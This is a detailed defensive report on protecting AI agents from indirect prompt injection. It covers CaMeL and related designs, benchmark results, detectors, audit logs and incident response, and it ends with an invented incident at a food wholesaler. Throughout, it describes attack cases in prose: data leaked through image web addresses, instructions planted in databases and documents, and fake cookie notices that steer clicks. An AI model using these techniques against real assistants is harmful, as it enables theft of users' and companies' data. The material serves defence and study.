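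For each argument *aᵢ* of a tool *t*, the policy specifies a set of accepted sources, *Tᵢ*. Let *A* be the set of people who would receive the data. The call *t*(*a*₁, …, *aₙ*) runs only if, for every argument,

*S*(*aᵢ*) ⊆ *Tᵢ* and *A* ⊆ *R*(*aᵢ*).

In the example, *S*(address) contains Bob's message, which is not an accepted source for a recipient. *A* contains the new address, which is not in *R*(file). This form is simplified. A CaMeL policy can be any Python function that returns "allow" or "deny" and a reason, so it could also, for example, limit the size of a payment.

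Both conditions are necessary. If a policy checked only the readers, an attacker's text could still trigger an action that reveals no data, such as deleting a file. If it checked only the sources, a user who typed the wrong address could send a confidential file to a stranger.

### What the design guarantees

Text from outside cannot add a step to the program, however persuasive it is, but it can influence which planned steps run if the program contains a condition such as "if Bob accepts, book the room". A tool call cannot violate its policy, provided the interpreter keeps correct records. Like the address check recommended for TicketOracle, these limits are in code, so they apply equally to new attacks.

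The content of a permitted message can still be false. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an assistant to email the day's schedule to their boss. A malicious calendar entry can rewrite the email but cannot change its recipient. An answer shown to the user can be false in the same way.

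Answers can also leak data if the policies cover only tool calls. Costa and colleagues treat responses to the user as harmless in their main design, but note that an application can also check responses that could cause harm. An assistant that displays images would need that check, because in EchoLeak the stolen data was sent out through an image in the answer.

A badly written policy can also let attacks through. If a policy treats every address in the user's contacts as trusted, and the mail program automatically adds anyone who writes to the user, an attacker can become a trusted recipient by sending one email, and the interpreter will enforce the policy as written. CaMeL also treats the user's request as trusted, so it offers no protection if the user pastes an attacker's text into the request.

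### Results on AgentDojo

Most tests of CaMeL use AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 ordinary tasks in simulated office, banking, travel and Slack accounts. It tests security by planting instructions in the data the agent reads during these tasks. In the latest version of their paper, Debenedetti and colleagues report that CaMeL solved 77% of the tasks with provable security, compared with 84% for an undefended system.

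Other measurements show greater drawbacks. Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025), in *Indirect Prompt Injections*, cite published CaMeL results for GPT-4o but could not fully reproduce them. *SecureClaw* (2026) presents a competing design and includes an adapted run of CaMeL's released code. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, ran CaMeL three times on the 16 banking tasks, with and without its policies.

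| Test of CaMeL | Tasks completed | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Bhagwatkar and colleagues, GPT-4o | 53.6% | 0% |
| *SecureClaw*, all tasks | 29.9% | 0 of 629 |
| Garby and colleagues, GPT-5.2, banking, policies off | 66.7% | 1 of 240 |
| Garby and colleagues, GPT-5.2, banking, policies on | 37.5% | 0 of 231 |

In Bhagwatkar and colleagues' own test, GPT-4o without a defence completed 83.0% of the tasks, and 57.7% of attacks succeeded. CaMeL stops the attacks in this benchmark, but the share of tasks it completes depends heavily on the model, the policies and how researchers connect it to the benchmark. The banking results are also imprecise because there are so few tasks. A benchmark has no user to approve a blocked payment, so in practice some of the failures would instead be requests for approval.

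CaMeL uses 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent, according to figures cited by Bhagwatkar and colleagues. Given the completion rates in the CaMeL paper, that is roughly three times as many tokens per completed task.

Bhagwatkar and colleagues also tested a much simpler defence, in which a second model removes suspicious instructions from everything the tools return. With GPT-4o, this filter also reduced successful attacks to zero, and the agent completed 74.1% of the tasks. These figures favour the filter over CaMeL, but Bhagwatkar and colleagues argue that AgentDojo's attacks are weak and that some of its scoring is faulty. Like the model guard for databases, the filter might miss a stronger attack, whereas CaMeL limits the steps an agent can take regardless of the attack's strength.

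### FIDES: choosing one step at a time

CaMeL's planning model writes the whole program in advance, while the planning model in FIDES chooses one tool call at a time and can see results from trusted sources. FIDES replaces untrusted results with variable names, so the model can, for example, pass an email to another tool without reading it.

Sometimes the assistant's next step depends on an email's content. Suppose a user asks it to check three emails and create a calendar event if one of them contains a meeting request. The planning model can query a quarantined model about whether any email contains one, and restrict the answer to "yes" or "no". An attacker can make the answer wrong, which might create an unwanted event, but cannot use it to pass on a new instruction. FIDES records the type of each value, so a policy can allow a yes-or-no answer from an untrusted email but still block free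 text from it.

Costa and colleagues compared FIDES with an ordinary agent on AgentDojo, using GPT-4o. The completion rates below are averages of their results for the four kinds of account, and the attack counts exclude cases that the benchmark scored incorrectly.

| Agent | Policies | Tasks completed without attacks | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary | Off | 84% | 152 |
| Ordinary | On | 42% | 0 |
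| FIDES | Off | 61% | 21 |
| FIDES | On | 50% | 0 |

The policies stopped the attacks in both agents. Hiding untrusted text let FIDES do more work under those policies, because an ordinary agent loses access to important tools as soon as it reads something untrusted. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES's lead over the ordinary agent grew from 8 to 16 percentage points.

Costa and colleagues prove that their method stops confidential data from flowing directly to people who aren't allowed to see it. The proof does not cover indirect leaks. For example, if an assistant contacts a lawyer only when an email mentions a lawsuit, anyone who sees that tool call can infer that the email mentions one.

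### Simpler patterns for narrower tasks

Many applications do not need an agent that can write programs. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, who include three of CaMeL's designers, describe six design patterns based on the principle that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any action with harmful side effects.

| Pattern | How the agent works | What planted text can still change |
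|---|---|---|
| Action selector | Chooses from fixed actions and never sees their results | Nothing, unless it is in the user's request |
| Plan then execute | Fixes a list of tool calls before reading any data | The content of those calls |
| Map-reduce | Gives each document to a separate model that returns a restricted answer | The answer about that document |
| Dual LLM | Plans with one model and reads with another | The values the reading model returns |
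| Code then execute | Writes a program first, as CaMeL does | The values the program handles |
| Context minimisation | Deletes the user's text before writing the answer | The action chosen from that text |

An online shop's assistant that only links to orders and settings pages can use the first pattern, which needs no provenance records. An agent that searches a folder for invoices can use the third pattern. The agent could mistake a malicious file for an invoice, but the file could not make the agent send other files.

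### Systems with several agents

Developers increasingly build systems in which one agent delegates work to others. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) shows that giving each agent its own CaMeL protection is not enough. Ilia Shumailov, a co-author, also worked on CaMeL.

In their experiment, a user asked a coordinating agent to send a summary of job applicants to a colleague on Slack. One agent fetched the records from a database and another sent the message. The researchers had planted an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address. The first two agents treated the records as untrusted. But the coordinating agent put the summary into its request to the messaging agent, which trusted the whole request as if it came from a user. The messaging agent's planning model read the planted instruction and added the email to its program.

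Peters-Gill and colleagues' solution, multi-CaMeL, splits each request into an instruction that the planning model reads and data that it can only refer to by name. The interpreter rejects any instruction that contains text derived from a tool's output. The researchers tested multi-CaMeL with 949 attacks on each of five models, using a multi-agent version of AgentDojo.

| Model | Attack success without CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
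|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0% | 0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0% | 0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 0% | 0% |

GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without CaMeL, so this test cannot show any security benefit for that model. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against reading too much into the result, because adaptive attackers in a large competition succeeded against every leading model tested. The experiments also used no data policies, so they tested only the limit on adding steps.

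### Gaps in the records and the policies

CaMeL's guarantees require the interpreter to track data correctly, and Garby and colleagues found cases where it does not. In a simplified example, a program sets `rich` to true, then changes it to false only if a secret bank balance is low. CaMeL marks a variable as secret only if the program makes such a change. If the balance is high, the program skips the change, so `rich` stays public even though its value reveals something about the balance. The program could then email that value to an outsider.

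An attacker cannot use an email to create such a program, because the planning model never reads the email. The leak would happen only if the planning model wrote such a program by chance or the user was malicious. The second gap is in how CaMeL retries after a failure. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit of secret data, and repeated attempts can reveal more. Error messages from one attempt also influence the next plan, and CaMeL censors them without a formal guarantee that this is enough. Garby and colleagues built an alternative interpreter with computer-checked proofs that it tracks these flows. Multi-CaMeL does not retry failed programs, but its interpreter inherits the first gap.

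CaMeL checks one tool call at a time, but some security rules also concern a whole plan. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that responds to security alerts and must get approval before disconnecting a computer from the network. CaMeL would detect a missing approval only at the last step, after a long and expensive investigation. CaMeLoT converts the program into a model of all its possible paths and checks them before anything runs. If a path breaks a rule, the planning model receives a description of that path and tries to repair the program. The check simplifies loops, so it sometimes rejects a safe plan.

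### Agents that operate a screen

Planning in advance is hardest for agents that click and type on a computer screen, because they normally look at the screen before each action. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026), the planning model writes a program that prepares for many possible screens. The average program had 213 lines and 41 tool calls, compared with 52 and 5 on AgentDojo. The protected agents kept at most 57% of the performance of leading models on OSWorld, a benchmark of computer tasks.

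They were still open to an attack that Foerster and colleagues call branch steering. A plan for browsing the web usually includes a step that closes cookie notices. An attacker can place an advertisement that looks like a cookie notice, and the reading model directs the click to it. The click is a planned step, so the program runs as written, but the agent ends up on the attacker's site. Ordinary policies help little here because the same click action can close a notice, delete a file or open a malicious page.

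### Rigidity and approvals

Critics object that such systems are too rigid for useful work. Costa and colleagues' classification implies that the right actions depend on what the agent reads in about a fifth of AgentDojo's tasks, and in over 40% of those for banking and Slack. For example, a user may ask the assistant to pay a bill by following the instructions in a file, which a policy against untrusted instructions forbids. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that most failed tasks needed an action that the program did not include. An ordinary agent could have added it after seeing the data.

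The other objection is that someone has to write and maintain the policies, and users have to respond to requests for approval. Willison warns that people who get these requests constantly start agreeing to everything. They will then eventually approve an action that serves an attacker.

CaMeL's designers accept much of this. They write that prompt injection attacks are "not fully solved", and they list policy maintenance and the risk of user fatigue among the limitations. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues defend the rigidity as deliberate. They think general-purpose agents built on current language models are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees, so they recommend that developers build agents for specific tasks and restrict them accordingly. They also suggest that tracking data explicitly could make approvals more efficient. Suppose an assistant makes 50 tool calls in a day, five of which send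 something out, and one of those five uses an address from an email. Asking the user about every call would mean 50 questions, asking about every outgoing message would mean five, and asking only when the recipient's address came from an email would mean one.

CaMeL also reduces task completion less when the model is stronger. On a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, Peters-Gill and colleagues found that CaMeL lowered completion by an average of 21.6 percentage points across the five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest. Even the smaller loss is large for an assistant that only drafts text for its user to check. It is easier to justify for an assistant that can make payments, where a single successful attack may do more harm than many unfinished tasks.

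Garby and colleagues offer a compromise in their own agent, Randori. Its planning model can mark a particular untrusted value as acceptable before it reads any outside data. If a user asks Randori to find a friend's payment details on the friend's website and send $50, the plan can allow the agent to use the account number from that page without asking the user again. With one model, Qwen3.7-plus, these exceptions raised completion of the banking tasks from 62.5% to 75%, although the sample was small. Across three models, only two of 1,296 attacks on Randori succeeded. Each exception removes the protection for that value, so anyone who can alter the friend's website can redirect the $50, but they cannot change the amount because it came from the user.

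## Detecting attacks in logs and live outputs

Designs like CaMeL limit what an attacker can make an assistant do, but they do not stop every attack. Organisations also need to detect attacks, as they happen and afterwards.

*How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks* (Microsoft, 2025) gives an unusually full account of how Microsoft protects a company assistant that reads employees' emails and documents, answers questions about them and can send messages. Some measures make injection less likely, such as inserting a special character between the words of an outside document so that the model can tell it apart from the user's request. Others detect injections or limit the harm from those that succeed.

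Some of these defences, such as blocking certain images and links, guarantee that a particular attack fails, but detection does not. Microsoft says that detecting every indirect injection with certainty is an open research challenge. A company should therefore keep records that let it later investigate the attacks its detectors miss.

### What a log has to record

If the assistant emails a confidential price list to a stranger, an investigator needs to find out which text caused this, what else the assistant sent, and whether other employees' assistants read the same text. The table compares the information needed to answer these questions with the main fields Microsoft documents for Copilot's audit record.

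| Information | What it shows | In Copilot's audit record |
|---|---|---|
| User's request | Whether the user asked for the action | The message's identifier, not its text |
| Retrieved sources | Which email or file contained the instructions | Each source's name, location and sensitivity label, and whether Microsoft detected an injection in it |
| Model and prompt version | How to repeat the attack in a test | Model and agent versions, but no prompt version |
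| Full output | Stolen data and hidden links | The message's identifier, not its text |
| Tool calls with arguments | What the assistant did, and to whom | The plugins enabled, but no arguments |
| Addresses contacted | Where the data went | Whether Copilot searched the web |
| Permissions used | What else the attacker could have reached | The user, and any policy that blocked access |

The record is most useful for tracing an attack to its source, but it does not include the chat text. Investigators can try to retrieve that text for a logged event with a separate Microsoft tool, or get the full requests and answers through an export interface.

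The log should keep a copy of each source as the model read it. The source's name may not be enough, because an attacker can edit a shared document after the attack. In the Cline case, someone retitled the GitHub issue afterward.

Addresses are harder to record, because the user's browser fetches the image and the assistant's server never receives the request. The application can record them by extracting every address from an answer before displaying it. A content security policy can also make the browser report each image it blocks, but this would have produced no reports in EchoLeak, because the policy allowed the address.

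All records of a task, including those from background services, need a shared identifier. In one ReLeak attack, data leaked up to eight minutes after the conversation ended. The agent must also be unable to alter the log. *Microsoft Fixes Copilot Audit Records* (Microsoft 365 for IT Pros, 2025) reports that AI audit logs have had gaps.

### The privacy cost of full logs

A complete log contains employees' questions about illness, pay and colleagues, as well as emails from people who never used the assistant. Splunk's *Getting Started With Copilot Log Analysis for Security in Microsoft 365* warns that showing this text to every administrator would be a major privacy violation. An intruder who took over one administrator's account could also search the log for company secrets.

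A company can reduce both risks by splitting the log in two. The general part holds identifiers, source names, tool names and the names of the sites contacted. The text goes into an encrypted store, which analysts can open only for a specific investigation and with a second person's approval. Full web addresses and tool arguments should go there too, because they may contain stolen data.

Microsoft keeps Copilot's audit logs for 180 days by default. A customer who learned of EchoLeak when it became public on 11 June 2025 could search back to 13 December 2024. 180 days may be too short to trace a false memory that went unused for months, but keeping text for longer exposes more of it if someone breaks in. One compromise is to delete the text early and keep the identifiers longer.

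The log contains text written by the attacker, so a web page that displays the log has to encode that text first, as any web page must with untrusted input. An AI tool that summarises the log may follow an instruction planted in it.

### Fixed rules on outputs

A program can check each answer for things that harmless answers rarely contain, such as a link to an unfamiliar site, a tag that runs a script, or the user's session token inside a link. The application knows the current token, so it can search for the exact value and its base64 form. Such rules are fast and usually precise enough to block an output automatically, and an analyst can see why one was triggered. The application should still record the blocked attempt, because it may show that an attacker's text has influenced the model.

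Fixed rules miss attacks their author did not anticipate. EchoLeak's image address began with the name of an approved Microsoft site. A six-digit login code looks like part of an ordinary web address. Gemini's false security warning contained no program code or link.

Rules that look for suspicious wording produce many false alarms. Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, searched web content for 3,963 phrases typical of prompt injections. They checked all 31,206 matches and confirmed 15,387, about half, as injections. Many of the others came from tutorials, documentation and news articles about prompt injection. Google ran a similar search and found that most matches were harmless for the same reason. A company's security team would trigger such a rule with its own emails about prompt injection.

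### Trained classifiers

A classifier learns from labelled examples and gives each text a score, so it can recognise attacks that do not use known phrases. Microsoft's Prompt Shields is a classifier for outside content, trained on known injection techniques in several languages. Its alerts appear in Microsoft's security portal, where analysts can compare them with other incidents. Classifiers can also examine outputs. The Morris II detector, for example, looked for copied text.

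Liu (2026), in *Passing the Test You Trained On*, tested 15 injection detectors on the data that agents receive from their tools. Liu ran the correct tool calls for simulated tasks without a model or an attacker, so the results were certain to be harmless. Some detectors flagged none of these results, but one flagged over 90% of them in one set of tasks. PIGuard gave the highest possible attack score to a message confirming a password change.

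Liu then planted attacks in the results and set each detector's threshold so that it wrongly flagged 1% of harmless items. The table shows the share of attacks that five of the detectors caught. AgentDojo is the benchmark used in most tests of CaMeL, BIPIA consists of emails, tables and code, and τ-bench simulates customer service.

| Detector | BIPIA | AgentDojo | τ-bench |
|---|---|---|---|
| PIGuard | 95.1% | 2.1% | 52.7% |
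| Prismor | 4.0% | 72.2% | 15.2% |
| Prompt Guard 2 (larger version) | 10.4% | 69.4% | 57.9% |
| Wolf Defender | 3.5% | 73.8% | 90.8% |
| Horizon-Labs | 37.7% | 82.2% | 100% |

The best detector on BIPIA was nearly useless on AgentDojo. PIGuard's training data included 1,116 emails, tables and code samples from BIPIA, though not the attacks in the test. It also included most of the attacks Liu used in τ-bench, but as short separate prompts. PIGuard caught 52.1% of the attacks that were in its training data and 55.8% of those that were not. Horizon-Labs's training data included none of these attacks, but it did include instructions planted in tool results. A company should therefore test a detector on its own assistant's data before relying on a published score.

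Large general-purpose models can also act as detectors. *BrowseSafe++* (Chen, Zhang et al., 2026) tested them on web pages, most of which contained injections that a browser agent had encountered in real use, and on a clean copy of each page. GPT-6 Astra had the best overall score among the large models but wrongly flagged 14% to 15% of the clean pages. Claude Opus 5.5 wrongly flagged only 4% to 5% but missed more attacks.

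A small detector that Chen and colleagues trained on similar pages did better than either. On HTML pages, it wrongly flagged 1.35% and caught about 98% of attacks, a figure calculated from the published accuracy. It cost about $0.18 per 1,000 pages, compared with at least $18.95 for the leading models. However, Chen and colleagues found the real injections with a classifier and a set of text patterns, then kept only those that other models recognised. Attacks that all these methods missed were not in the test, so the true catch rate is probably lower.

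The same experiment supports running detection separately from the assistant's main task. In 74% of the cases where a model followed an injection, the same model had flagged it when asked only to look for attacks.

Attackers who adapt are a greater problem. Liu used fixed attacks and therefore calls the catch rates upper limits. Chen and colleagues tested adaptive attacks on browser agents, not on detectors. The original injections succeeded in at most 4% of tasks, but when a program revised them in response to each failure, they succeeded in 31% to 95%, depending on the agent. Detectors that examine a model's internal activity instead of its text are also vulnerable. *Beyond AUROC* (2026) cites earlier work in which attackers who knew about such a detector evaded it.

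Willison argues that a filter that catches 99% of attacks is "effectively worthless", because an attacker needs only one success. This is a strong argument against relying on a filter alone, but a weaker one against using a filter as an alarm, since an attacker who fails 99 times may produce 99 alerts before succeeding. But many detectors are free to download, so an attacker can practise on a private copy without alerting anyone.

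An application should also not relax other checks because a detector gives a low score. *Confidently Wrong* (2026) examines attacks that a detector rates as very unlikely to be attacks. If the application skips the user's approval because of such a score, the attack is easier than it would be without the detector.

### Unusual sequences of tool calls

An attack may look harmless in each output but still make an AI assistant behave unusually over a whole task. An assistant often searches for an email, reads it and answers, but it rarely reads a stranger's email, searches the mailbox for passwords and then writes to a new recipient. If it has taken those steps in that order in only two of 200,000 completed tasks, the next occurrence deserves attention.

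Microsoft advises developers to assume that injections will happen and recommends this kind of behavioural monitoring as one defence. OWASP warns that improper output handling can do more harm if nobody monitors for anomalies.

This method needs no examples of attacks, but it misses those that follow a normal sequence. In EchoLeak, Copilot searched for material and answered a question, as it normally does. A payment to a false account uses the same tools as a genuine one, so the monitor also has to check the arguments, for example by comparing the account number with those used in earlier payments.

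New features and unusual work, such as preparing annual accounts, can cause false alarms. So can rare events in a large company. If the company runs a million tasks a day, a sequence that occurs once in 10,000 tasks will appear about 100 times daily.

### Planted false secrets

A company can place a false secret, such as a password for an account that nobody uses, in an email or document. No ordinary task needs it, so its appearance in an outgoing message or web address suggests theft. The company can also raise an alarm if anyone tries to log in with the password. This works even if the attacker encoded the password to hide it from checks on outgoing text, because they have to decode it to log in.

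False alarms are rare but possible. An employee who asks the assistant for all the passwords in a mailbox will receive the fake one and may try it. Labeling the password as fake would prevent this but also warn an attacker.

The chance of catching an attacker depends on how much they steal. Suppose ten of the 10,000 emails in a mailbox contain fake secrets, and the attacker steals emails at random.

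| Emails stolen | Chance that at least one contains a false secret |
|---|---|
| 1 | 0.1% |
| 100 | 10% |
| 1,000 | 65% |

False secrets are more likely to detect an attacker who asks for the most sensitive information, as in EchoLeak, than one who wants something specific, such as the latest login code. This is because a false password may look like the most sensitive information available. False secrets cannot detect attacks that steal nothing, such as those that produce a false answer or delete a file.

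### The arithmetic of false alarms

Suppose the assistant and its copies produce 1,000,000 outputs a day, 100 of them malicious, and a detector catches 95% of the malicious ones. The table shows the results for three false positive rates, assuming an analyst needs five minutes for each alarm.

| False positive rate | True alarms | False alarms | Share of alarms that are real | Review time per day |
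|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 95 | About 10,000 | 0.9% | 841 hours |
| 0.1% | 95 | About 1,000 | 8.7% | 91 hours |
| 0.01% | 95 | About 100 | 49% | 16 hours |

At a false positive rate of 1%, the company would need about 105 analysts working eight hours a day, and they would find one attack in every 106 alarms. They would probably start dismissing alarms without reading them. At 0.01%, two analysts could do the work, and about half the alarms would be real attacks.

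In general, if *p* is the share of outputs that are malicious, *t* the share of these that the detector catches and *f* the false positive rate, the share of alarms that are real is

*pt* / (*pt* + (1 − *p*)*f*).

When attacks are rare, lowering *f* helps far more than raising *t*. A detector that caught every attack would find only five more a day, whereas reducing the false positive rate from 1% to 0.01% would remove about 9,900 false alarms. *Beyond AUROC* uses 1% as its stricter setting because false alarms take up analysts' time, but even 1% is far too high at this volume.

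Automatic blocking needs no analysts, but users lose harmless answers when the detector wrongly flags them. An employee who receives 20 harmless answers a day would lose at least one on 18% of days at a false positive rate of 1%, and on 0.2% of days at 0.01%. *Prompt Injection Detection is Regime-Dependent* (2026) notes that a detector with acceptable overall scores may still be unsuitable if it blocks too many legitimate prompts.

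False alarms disrupt agents more, because one blocked tool result can stop a whole task. In Liu's tests on AgentDojo, the detector ProtectAI v2 flagged 30% of harmless results, which would have stopped 69% of tasks. When an alarm is uncertain, the application can remove a link or ask the user to confirm an action, and block automatically only when a precise rule matches.

The company can also apply the detector to fewer outputs, such as those that send anything outside the company. Suppose only 10,000 of the million outputs do this, and all 100 malicious ones are among them. A detector with a false positive rate of 1% then raises only 99 false alarms. But nobody checks for false answers shown to employees.

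Requiring two detectors to agree could also reduce false alarms. If each wrongly flags 1% of harmless outputs and their errors are independent, both will flag the same harmless output only 0.01% of the time. But if each catches 95% of attacks, both will flag only about 90% of them. Detectors also often share weaknesses, such as flagging anything that contains a lot of web code, so the real reduction in false alarms may be much smaller.

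A very low false positive rate is difficult to prove. If a detector makes no errors, the upper limit on its error rate is roughly three divided by the number of trials, so it has to process about 30,000 independent harmless outputs without flagging any to show that its rate is below 0.01%. Horizon-Labs made no errors on AgentDojo's 339 harmless results, which is compatible with a true rate as high as 0.9%, or nearly 9,000 false alarms a day in this example. On τ-bench, it flagged 0.7% of harmless results.

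Chen and colleagues' data show the same problem in a real product. Over about a year, a classifier flagged roughly 603,000 of the pages that the browser agent read, and text patterns supplied more. After removing duplicates, Chen and colleagues had three models vote on about 1.09 million pages, and only 58,036 (5.3%) received enough votes to count as attacks. Even if the classifier had flagged all of these, at most about 11% of its alarms would have been real. The models may have rejected some genuine attacks, but probably too few to change this conclusion.

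### How often attacks occur

The figure of 100 malicious outputs in the example is an assumption. Published evidence consists mostly of counts of planted instructions, not successful attacks, and much of it comes from companies that sell security products.

Khodayari and colleagues provide the largest independent count of injections in web pages. They confirmed injections on 9,676 pages among 1.2 billion web addresses from an October 2025 archive, or about eight per million. Website operators wrote 81% of these injections, and many were meant to disrupt or identify AI programs that read the site. Across all their sources, 54 templates accounted for 95% of the injections. In tests on 13 models, the injections worked at most 8% of the time. Because the search relied on known phrases, it would have missed attacks written as ordinary prose.

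Google's survey of the same archive also found mainly pranks, attempts to promote businesses and messages meant to keep AI systems away. The few attempts to steal data were unsophisticated. However, malicious injections rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. Google develops AI assistants and sells security services, but its findings on sophistication match those of the independent study.

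Security vendors describe a more serious threat. *Fooling AI Agents*, by Palo Alto Networks' research team Unit 42, states that attackers are "actively" using web injections as weapons. Its main example is a scam advertisement with hidden text telling an AI reviewer to approve it, but Unit 42 knows of no confirmed case where this worked on a deployed reviewer. *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that Zscaler, another vendor, found websites with hidden text intended to make agents send cryptocurrency payments.

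Some injections come from companies promoting themselves rather than from criminals. Microsoft, which sells security products, found more than 50 different prompts from 31 companies behind "Summarize with AI" buttons. Clicking one of these buttons runs a prompt intended to make the assistant remember the company as a trusted source or recommend it first.

Surveys of public websites show little about attacks on AI assistants that read private email. The closest evidence is an analysis by the email security vendor Barracuda, described in *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026). Barracuda examined a phishing campaign in which each message contained a password-protected attachment for the recipient and hidden instructions for the recipient's AI assistant. Even if the recipient ignored the email, the assistant's summary could present it as urgent. Barracuda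 did not say how widespread the campaign was.

A company can better estimate how many attacks arrive by mail and how many its assistant follows by searching its own mail for hidden instructions and comparing the results with the assistant's outputs. It can then send harmless test attacks at random times to measure how many its detectors miss.

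## Response plans and duties to report

A company that discovers an attack has to stop it, find out how far it reached and tell the people affected. Several organisations have published plans for this, most of which build on a general guide from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST).

### The published plans

*Incident Response Recommendations and Considerations for Cybersecurity Risk Management* (Nelson, Rekhi and colleagues, 2025), NIST's SP 800-61 Revision 3, spreads incident response across an organisation's whole security programme. When NIST wrote the previous version in 2012, a separate team could usually finish a response in a day or two, but recovery now often takes weeks or months. Three functions (govern, identify and protect) cover preparation, and three more (detect, respond and recover) cover the incident itself. The guide covers computer systems in general,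 so it does not explain how to clean an AI assistant's memory or search index.

OWASP's *GenAI Incident Response Guide* (2025) includes a way to rank AI incidents by severity. Staff score an incident from 1 to 4 on five dimensions, such as its effect on data, and the highest score decides the rank. A serious data leak therefore counts as critical even if the assistant otherwise works normally. OWASP's example targets for a critical incident are to start containing it within 15 minutes, remove the cause within four hours and restore the service within eight.

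The Coalition for Secure AI's *AI Incident Response Framework, V1.0* (2025) matches containment to the type of system. Staff reset an assistant's memory if it has one, quarantine the sources of an assistant that searches documents, and disable an agent's tools. For a plain chatbot, the measures include lowering the temperature, a setting that controls how randomly the model chooses its words. Lowering the temperature is weak protection against prompt injection, because a less random model may follow the planted instruction more consistently.

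The framework also includes sample playbooks that security software can read and partly run. In the prompt injection playbook, the response to a malicious document is to filter it, alert the security team and record the incident. The playbook has no step for finding other conversations that used the same document, although the framework's general advice is to identify all affected users and data.

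The *JCDC AI Cybersecurity Collaboration Playbook*, published in January 2025 by the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA), explains how companies can voluntarily share information about AI incidents and vulnerabilities with the agency and with each other. It is useful for deciding what to send and to whom, but not for running the response.

The main addition in 2026 is NIST, NSA and CISA's *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response in Super Intelligence Training*, a set of ten voluntary practices published in October. ("Super intelligence" is the term these agencies now use for AI.) It mainly concerns agents that take significant actions nobody told them to take. Its definition excludes actions directed by an attacker, such as through prompt injection, but its advice on evidence and on checks before restarting an agent is useful in both cases.

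NIST's cybersecurity profile for AI is still unfinished. NIST released a preliminary draft by Megas, Cuthill and colleagues on 16 December 2025, according to Inside Privacy's *NIST Publishes Preliminary Draft of Cybersecurity Framework Profile for Artificial Intelligence*. The draft applies NIST's general security framework to protecting AI systems, using AI for defence and resisting attacks that use AI. NIST was still reviewing comments in mid-November 2026, according to its *Cyber SI Profile* page. It also announced in *Workshop on SI Incident Management* (2026) that it plans to update SP 800-61.

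### An invented incident: the first hour

Suppose a food wholesaler in the EU has built an assistant on a model it accesses through a provider's online interface. The assistant searches emails and shared folders, answers employees' questions and can send messages. On a Thursday afternoon, an attacker uses a supplier's stolen account to upload a price list containing hidden instructions for the model to put private information into the web address of an image, as in EchoLeak.

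At 08:50 on Monday, an employee reports a broken image in an answer. A security analyst opens the stored answer and finds that the image's URL points to an unfamiliar site. The URL contains a customer's name and email address, and a password for the wholesaler's delivery system. By 09:20 the analyst is confident that the data has left the company and declares an incident. The wholesaler scores the effect on data as 4, which makes the incident critical.

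By 09:30 the team that runs the assistant has turned off external images, email sending and web access for everyone. It has also stopped the assistant from searching suppliers' folders, because the document could still put a false price or a dangerous link into an answer. Employees can still ask about internal files.

This takes only ten minutes because the developers built a separate switch for each feature. Without them, the team would have to take the whole assistant offline, which managers may hesitate to approve. In the Coalition for Secure AI's example division of roles, the incident commander is accountable for taking a model offline and consults the legal team first. Doing both within OWASP's 15 minutes is hard, so the company should decide in advance which features staff can turn off without asking.

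The security team then changes the delivery system's password and tries the old one to confirm that it no longer works, the check that Cline missed. The team also looks for logins since Thursday that used the old password. If the assistant's own access keys ever appeared in a prompt, the team has to replace those too.

### Preserving evidence

The Coalition for Secure AI recommends making forensic copies before containing an incident. The wholesaler was still right to turn off the pictures before making copies, because this destroys no evidence and any delay could leak more data. But deleting the price list or resetting the assistant's memory would destroy evidence, so staff need to copy these first.

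Between 09:40 and 10:30, the security team copies:

- the price list, and the passages from it in the search index
- stored answers and tool calls since Thursday
- the assistant's memory and saved (cached) answers
- the application's settings and the version of the model.

The organization records who made each copy and when, and computes a digital fingerprint so it can later show that nobody changed the file. It also asks the model provider to keep its own records of the requests.

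Some organisations leave an attacker in a controlled environment for a while to learn more. Nelson and colleagues advise discussing this with the legal department first, since the attacker could use the delay to reach other systems. The wholesaler would gain little from leaving the attacker in place, because the attacker only has to wait for data to arrive.

### Finding every affected conversation

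At 10:30 the team searches the logs for every conversation in which the assistant read the price list, and finds 43. It then searches all answers since Thursday for the attacker's web address and finds three more conversations, in which the assistant read meeting notes instead of the price list. An employee had pasted one of the assistant's answers into those notes, and that answer quoted the hidden instruction.

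If the team had searched only for the original document, they would have missed the meeting notes, and the data leak could have resumed once they turned pictures back on. Nelson and colleagues warn that if responders check only the known targets, an incident can continue elsewhere unnoticed.

Of the 46 conversations, 12 contain a picture at the attacker's address. In three of these, the model added the picture but no private data. The other nine contain the contact details of 140 customers and the password. The office network's records show that employees' browsers requested seven of the nine pictures. The other two employees were working from home, where the company has no such records, so it must assume that the attacker received the data from all nine.

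The team also reads the 34 conversations without a picture, because the planted text could have had other effects. In two of them, the assistant saved a note from the price list to its long-term memory.

### Removing the planted text

By 14:00 the team knows where the text is and can start removing it, beginning with the price list in its shared folder. The wholesaler's search index rebuilds itself from the shared folders every night, so if staff removed the passages only from the index, the passages would be back on Tuesday morning.

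1. Staff move the price list and the meeting notes to a quarantined folder that the assistant cannot search.
2. They delete every passage of both documents from the index.
3. They clear the cached answers, which the application would otherwise reuse for similar questions.
4. They delete the two notes from the assistant's memory.
5. They close all 46 conversations, because an open one would keep supplying the planted text to the model.

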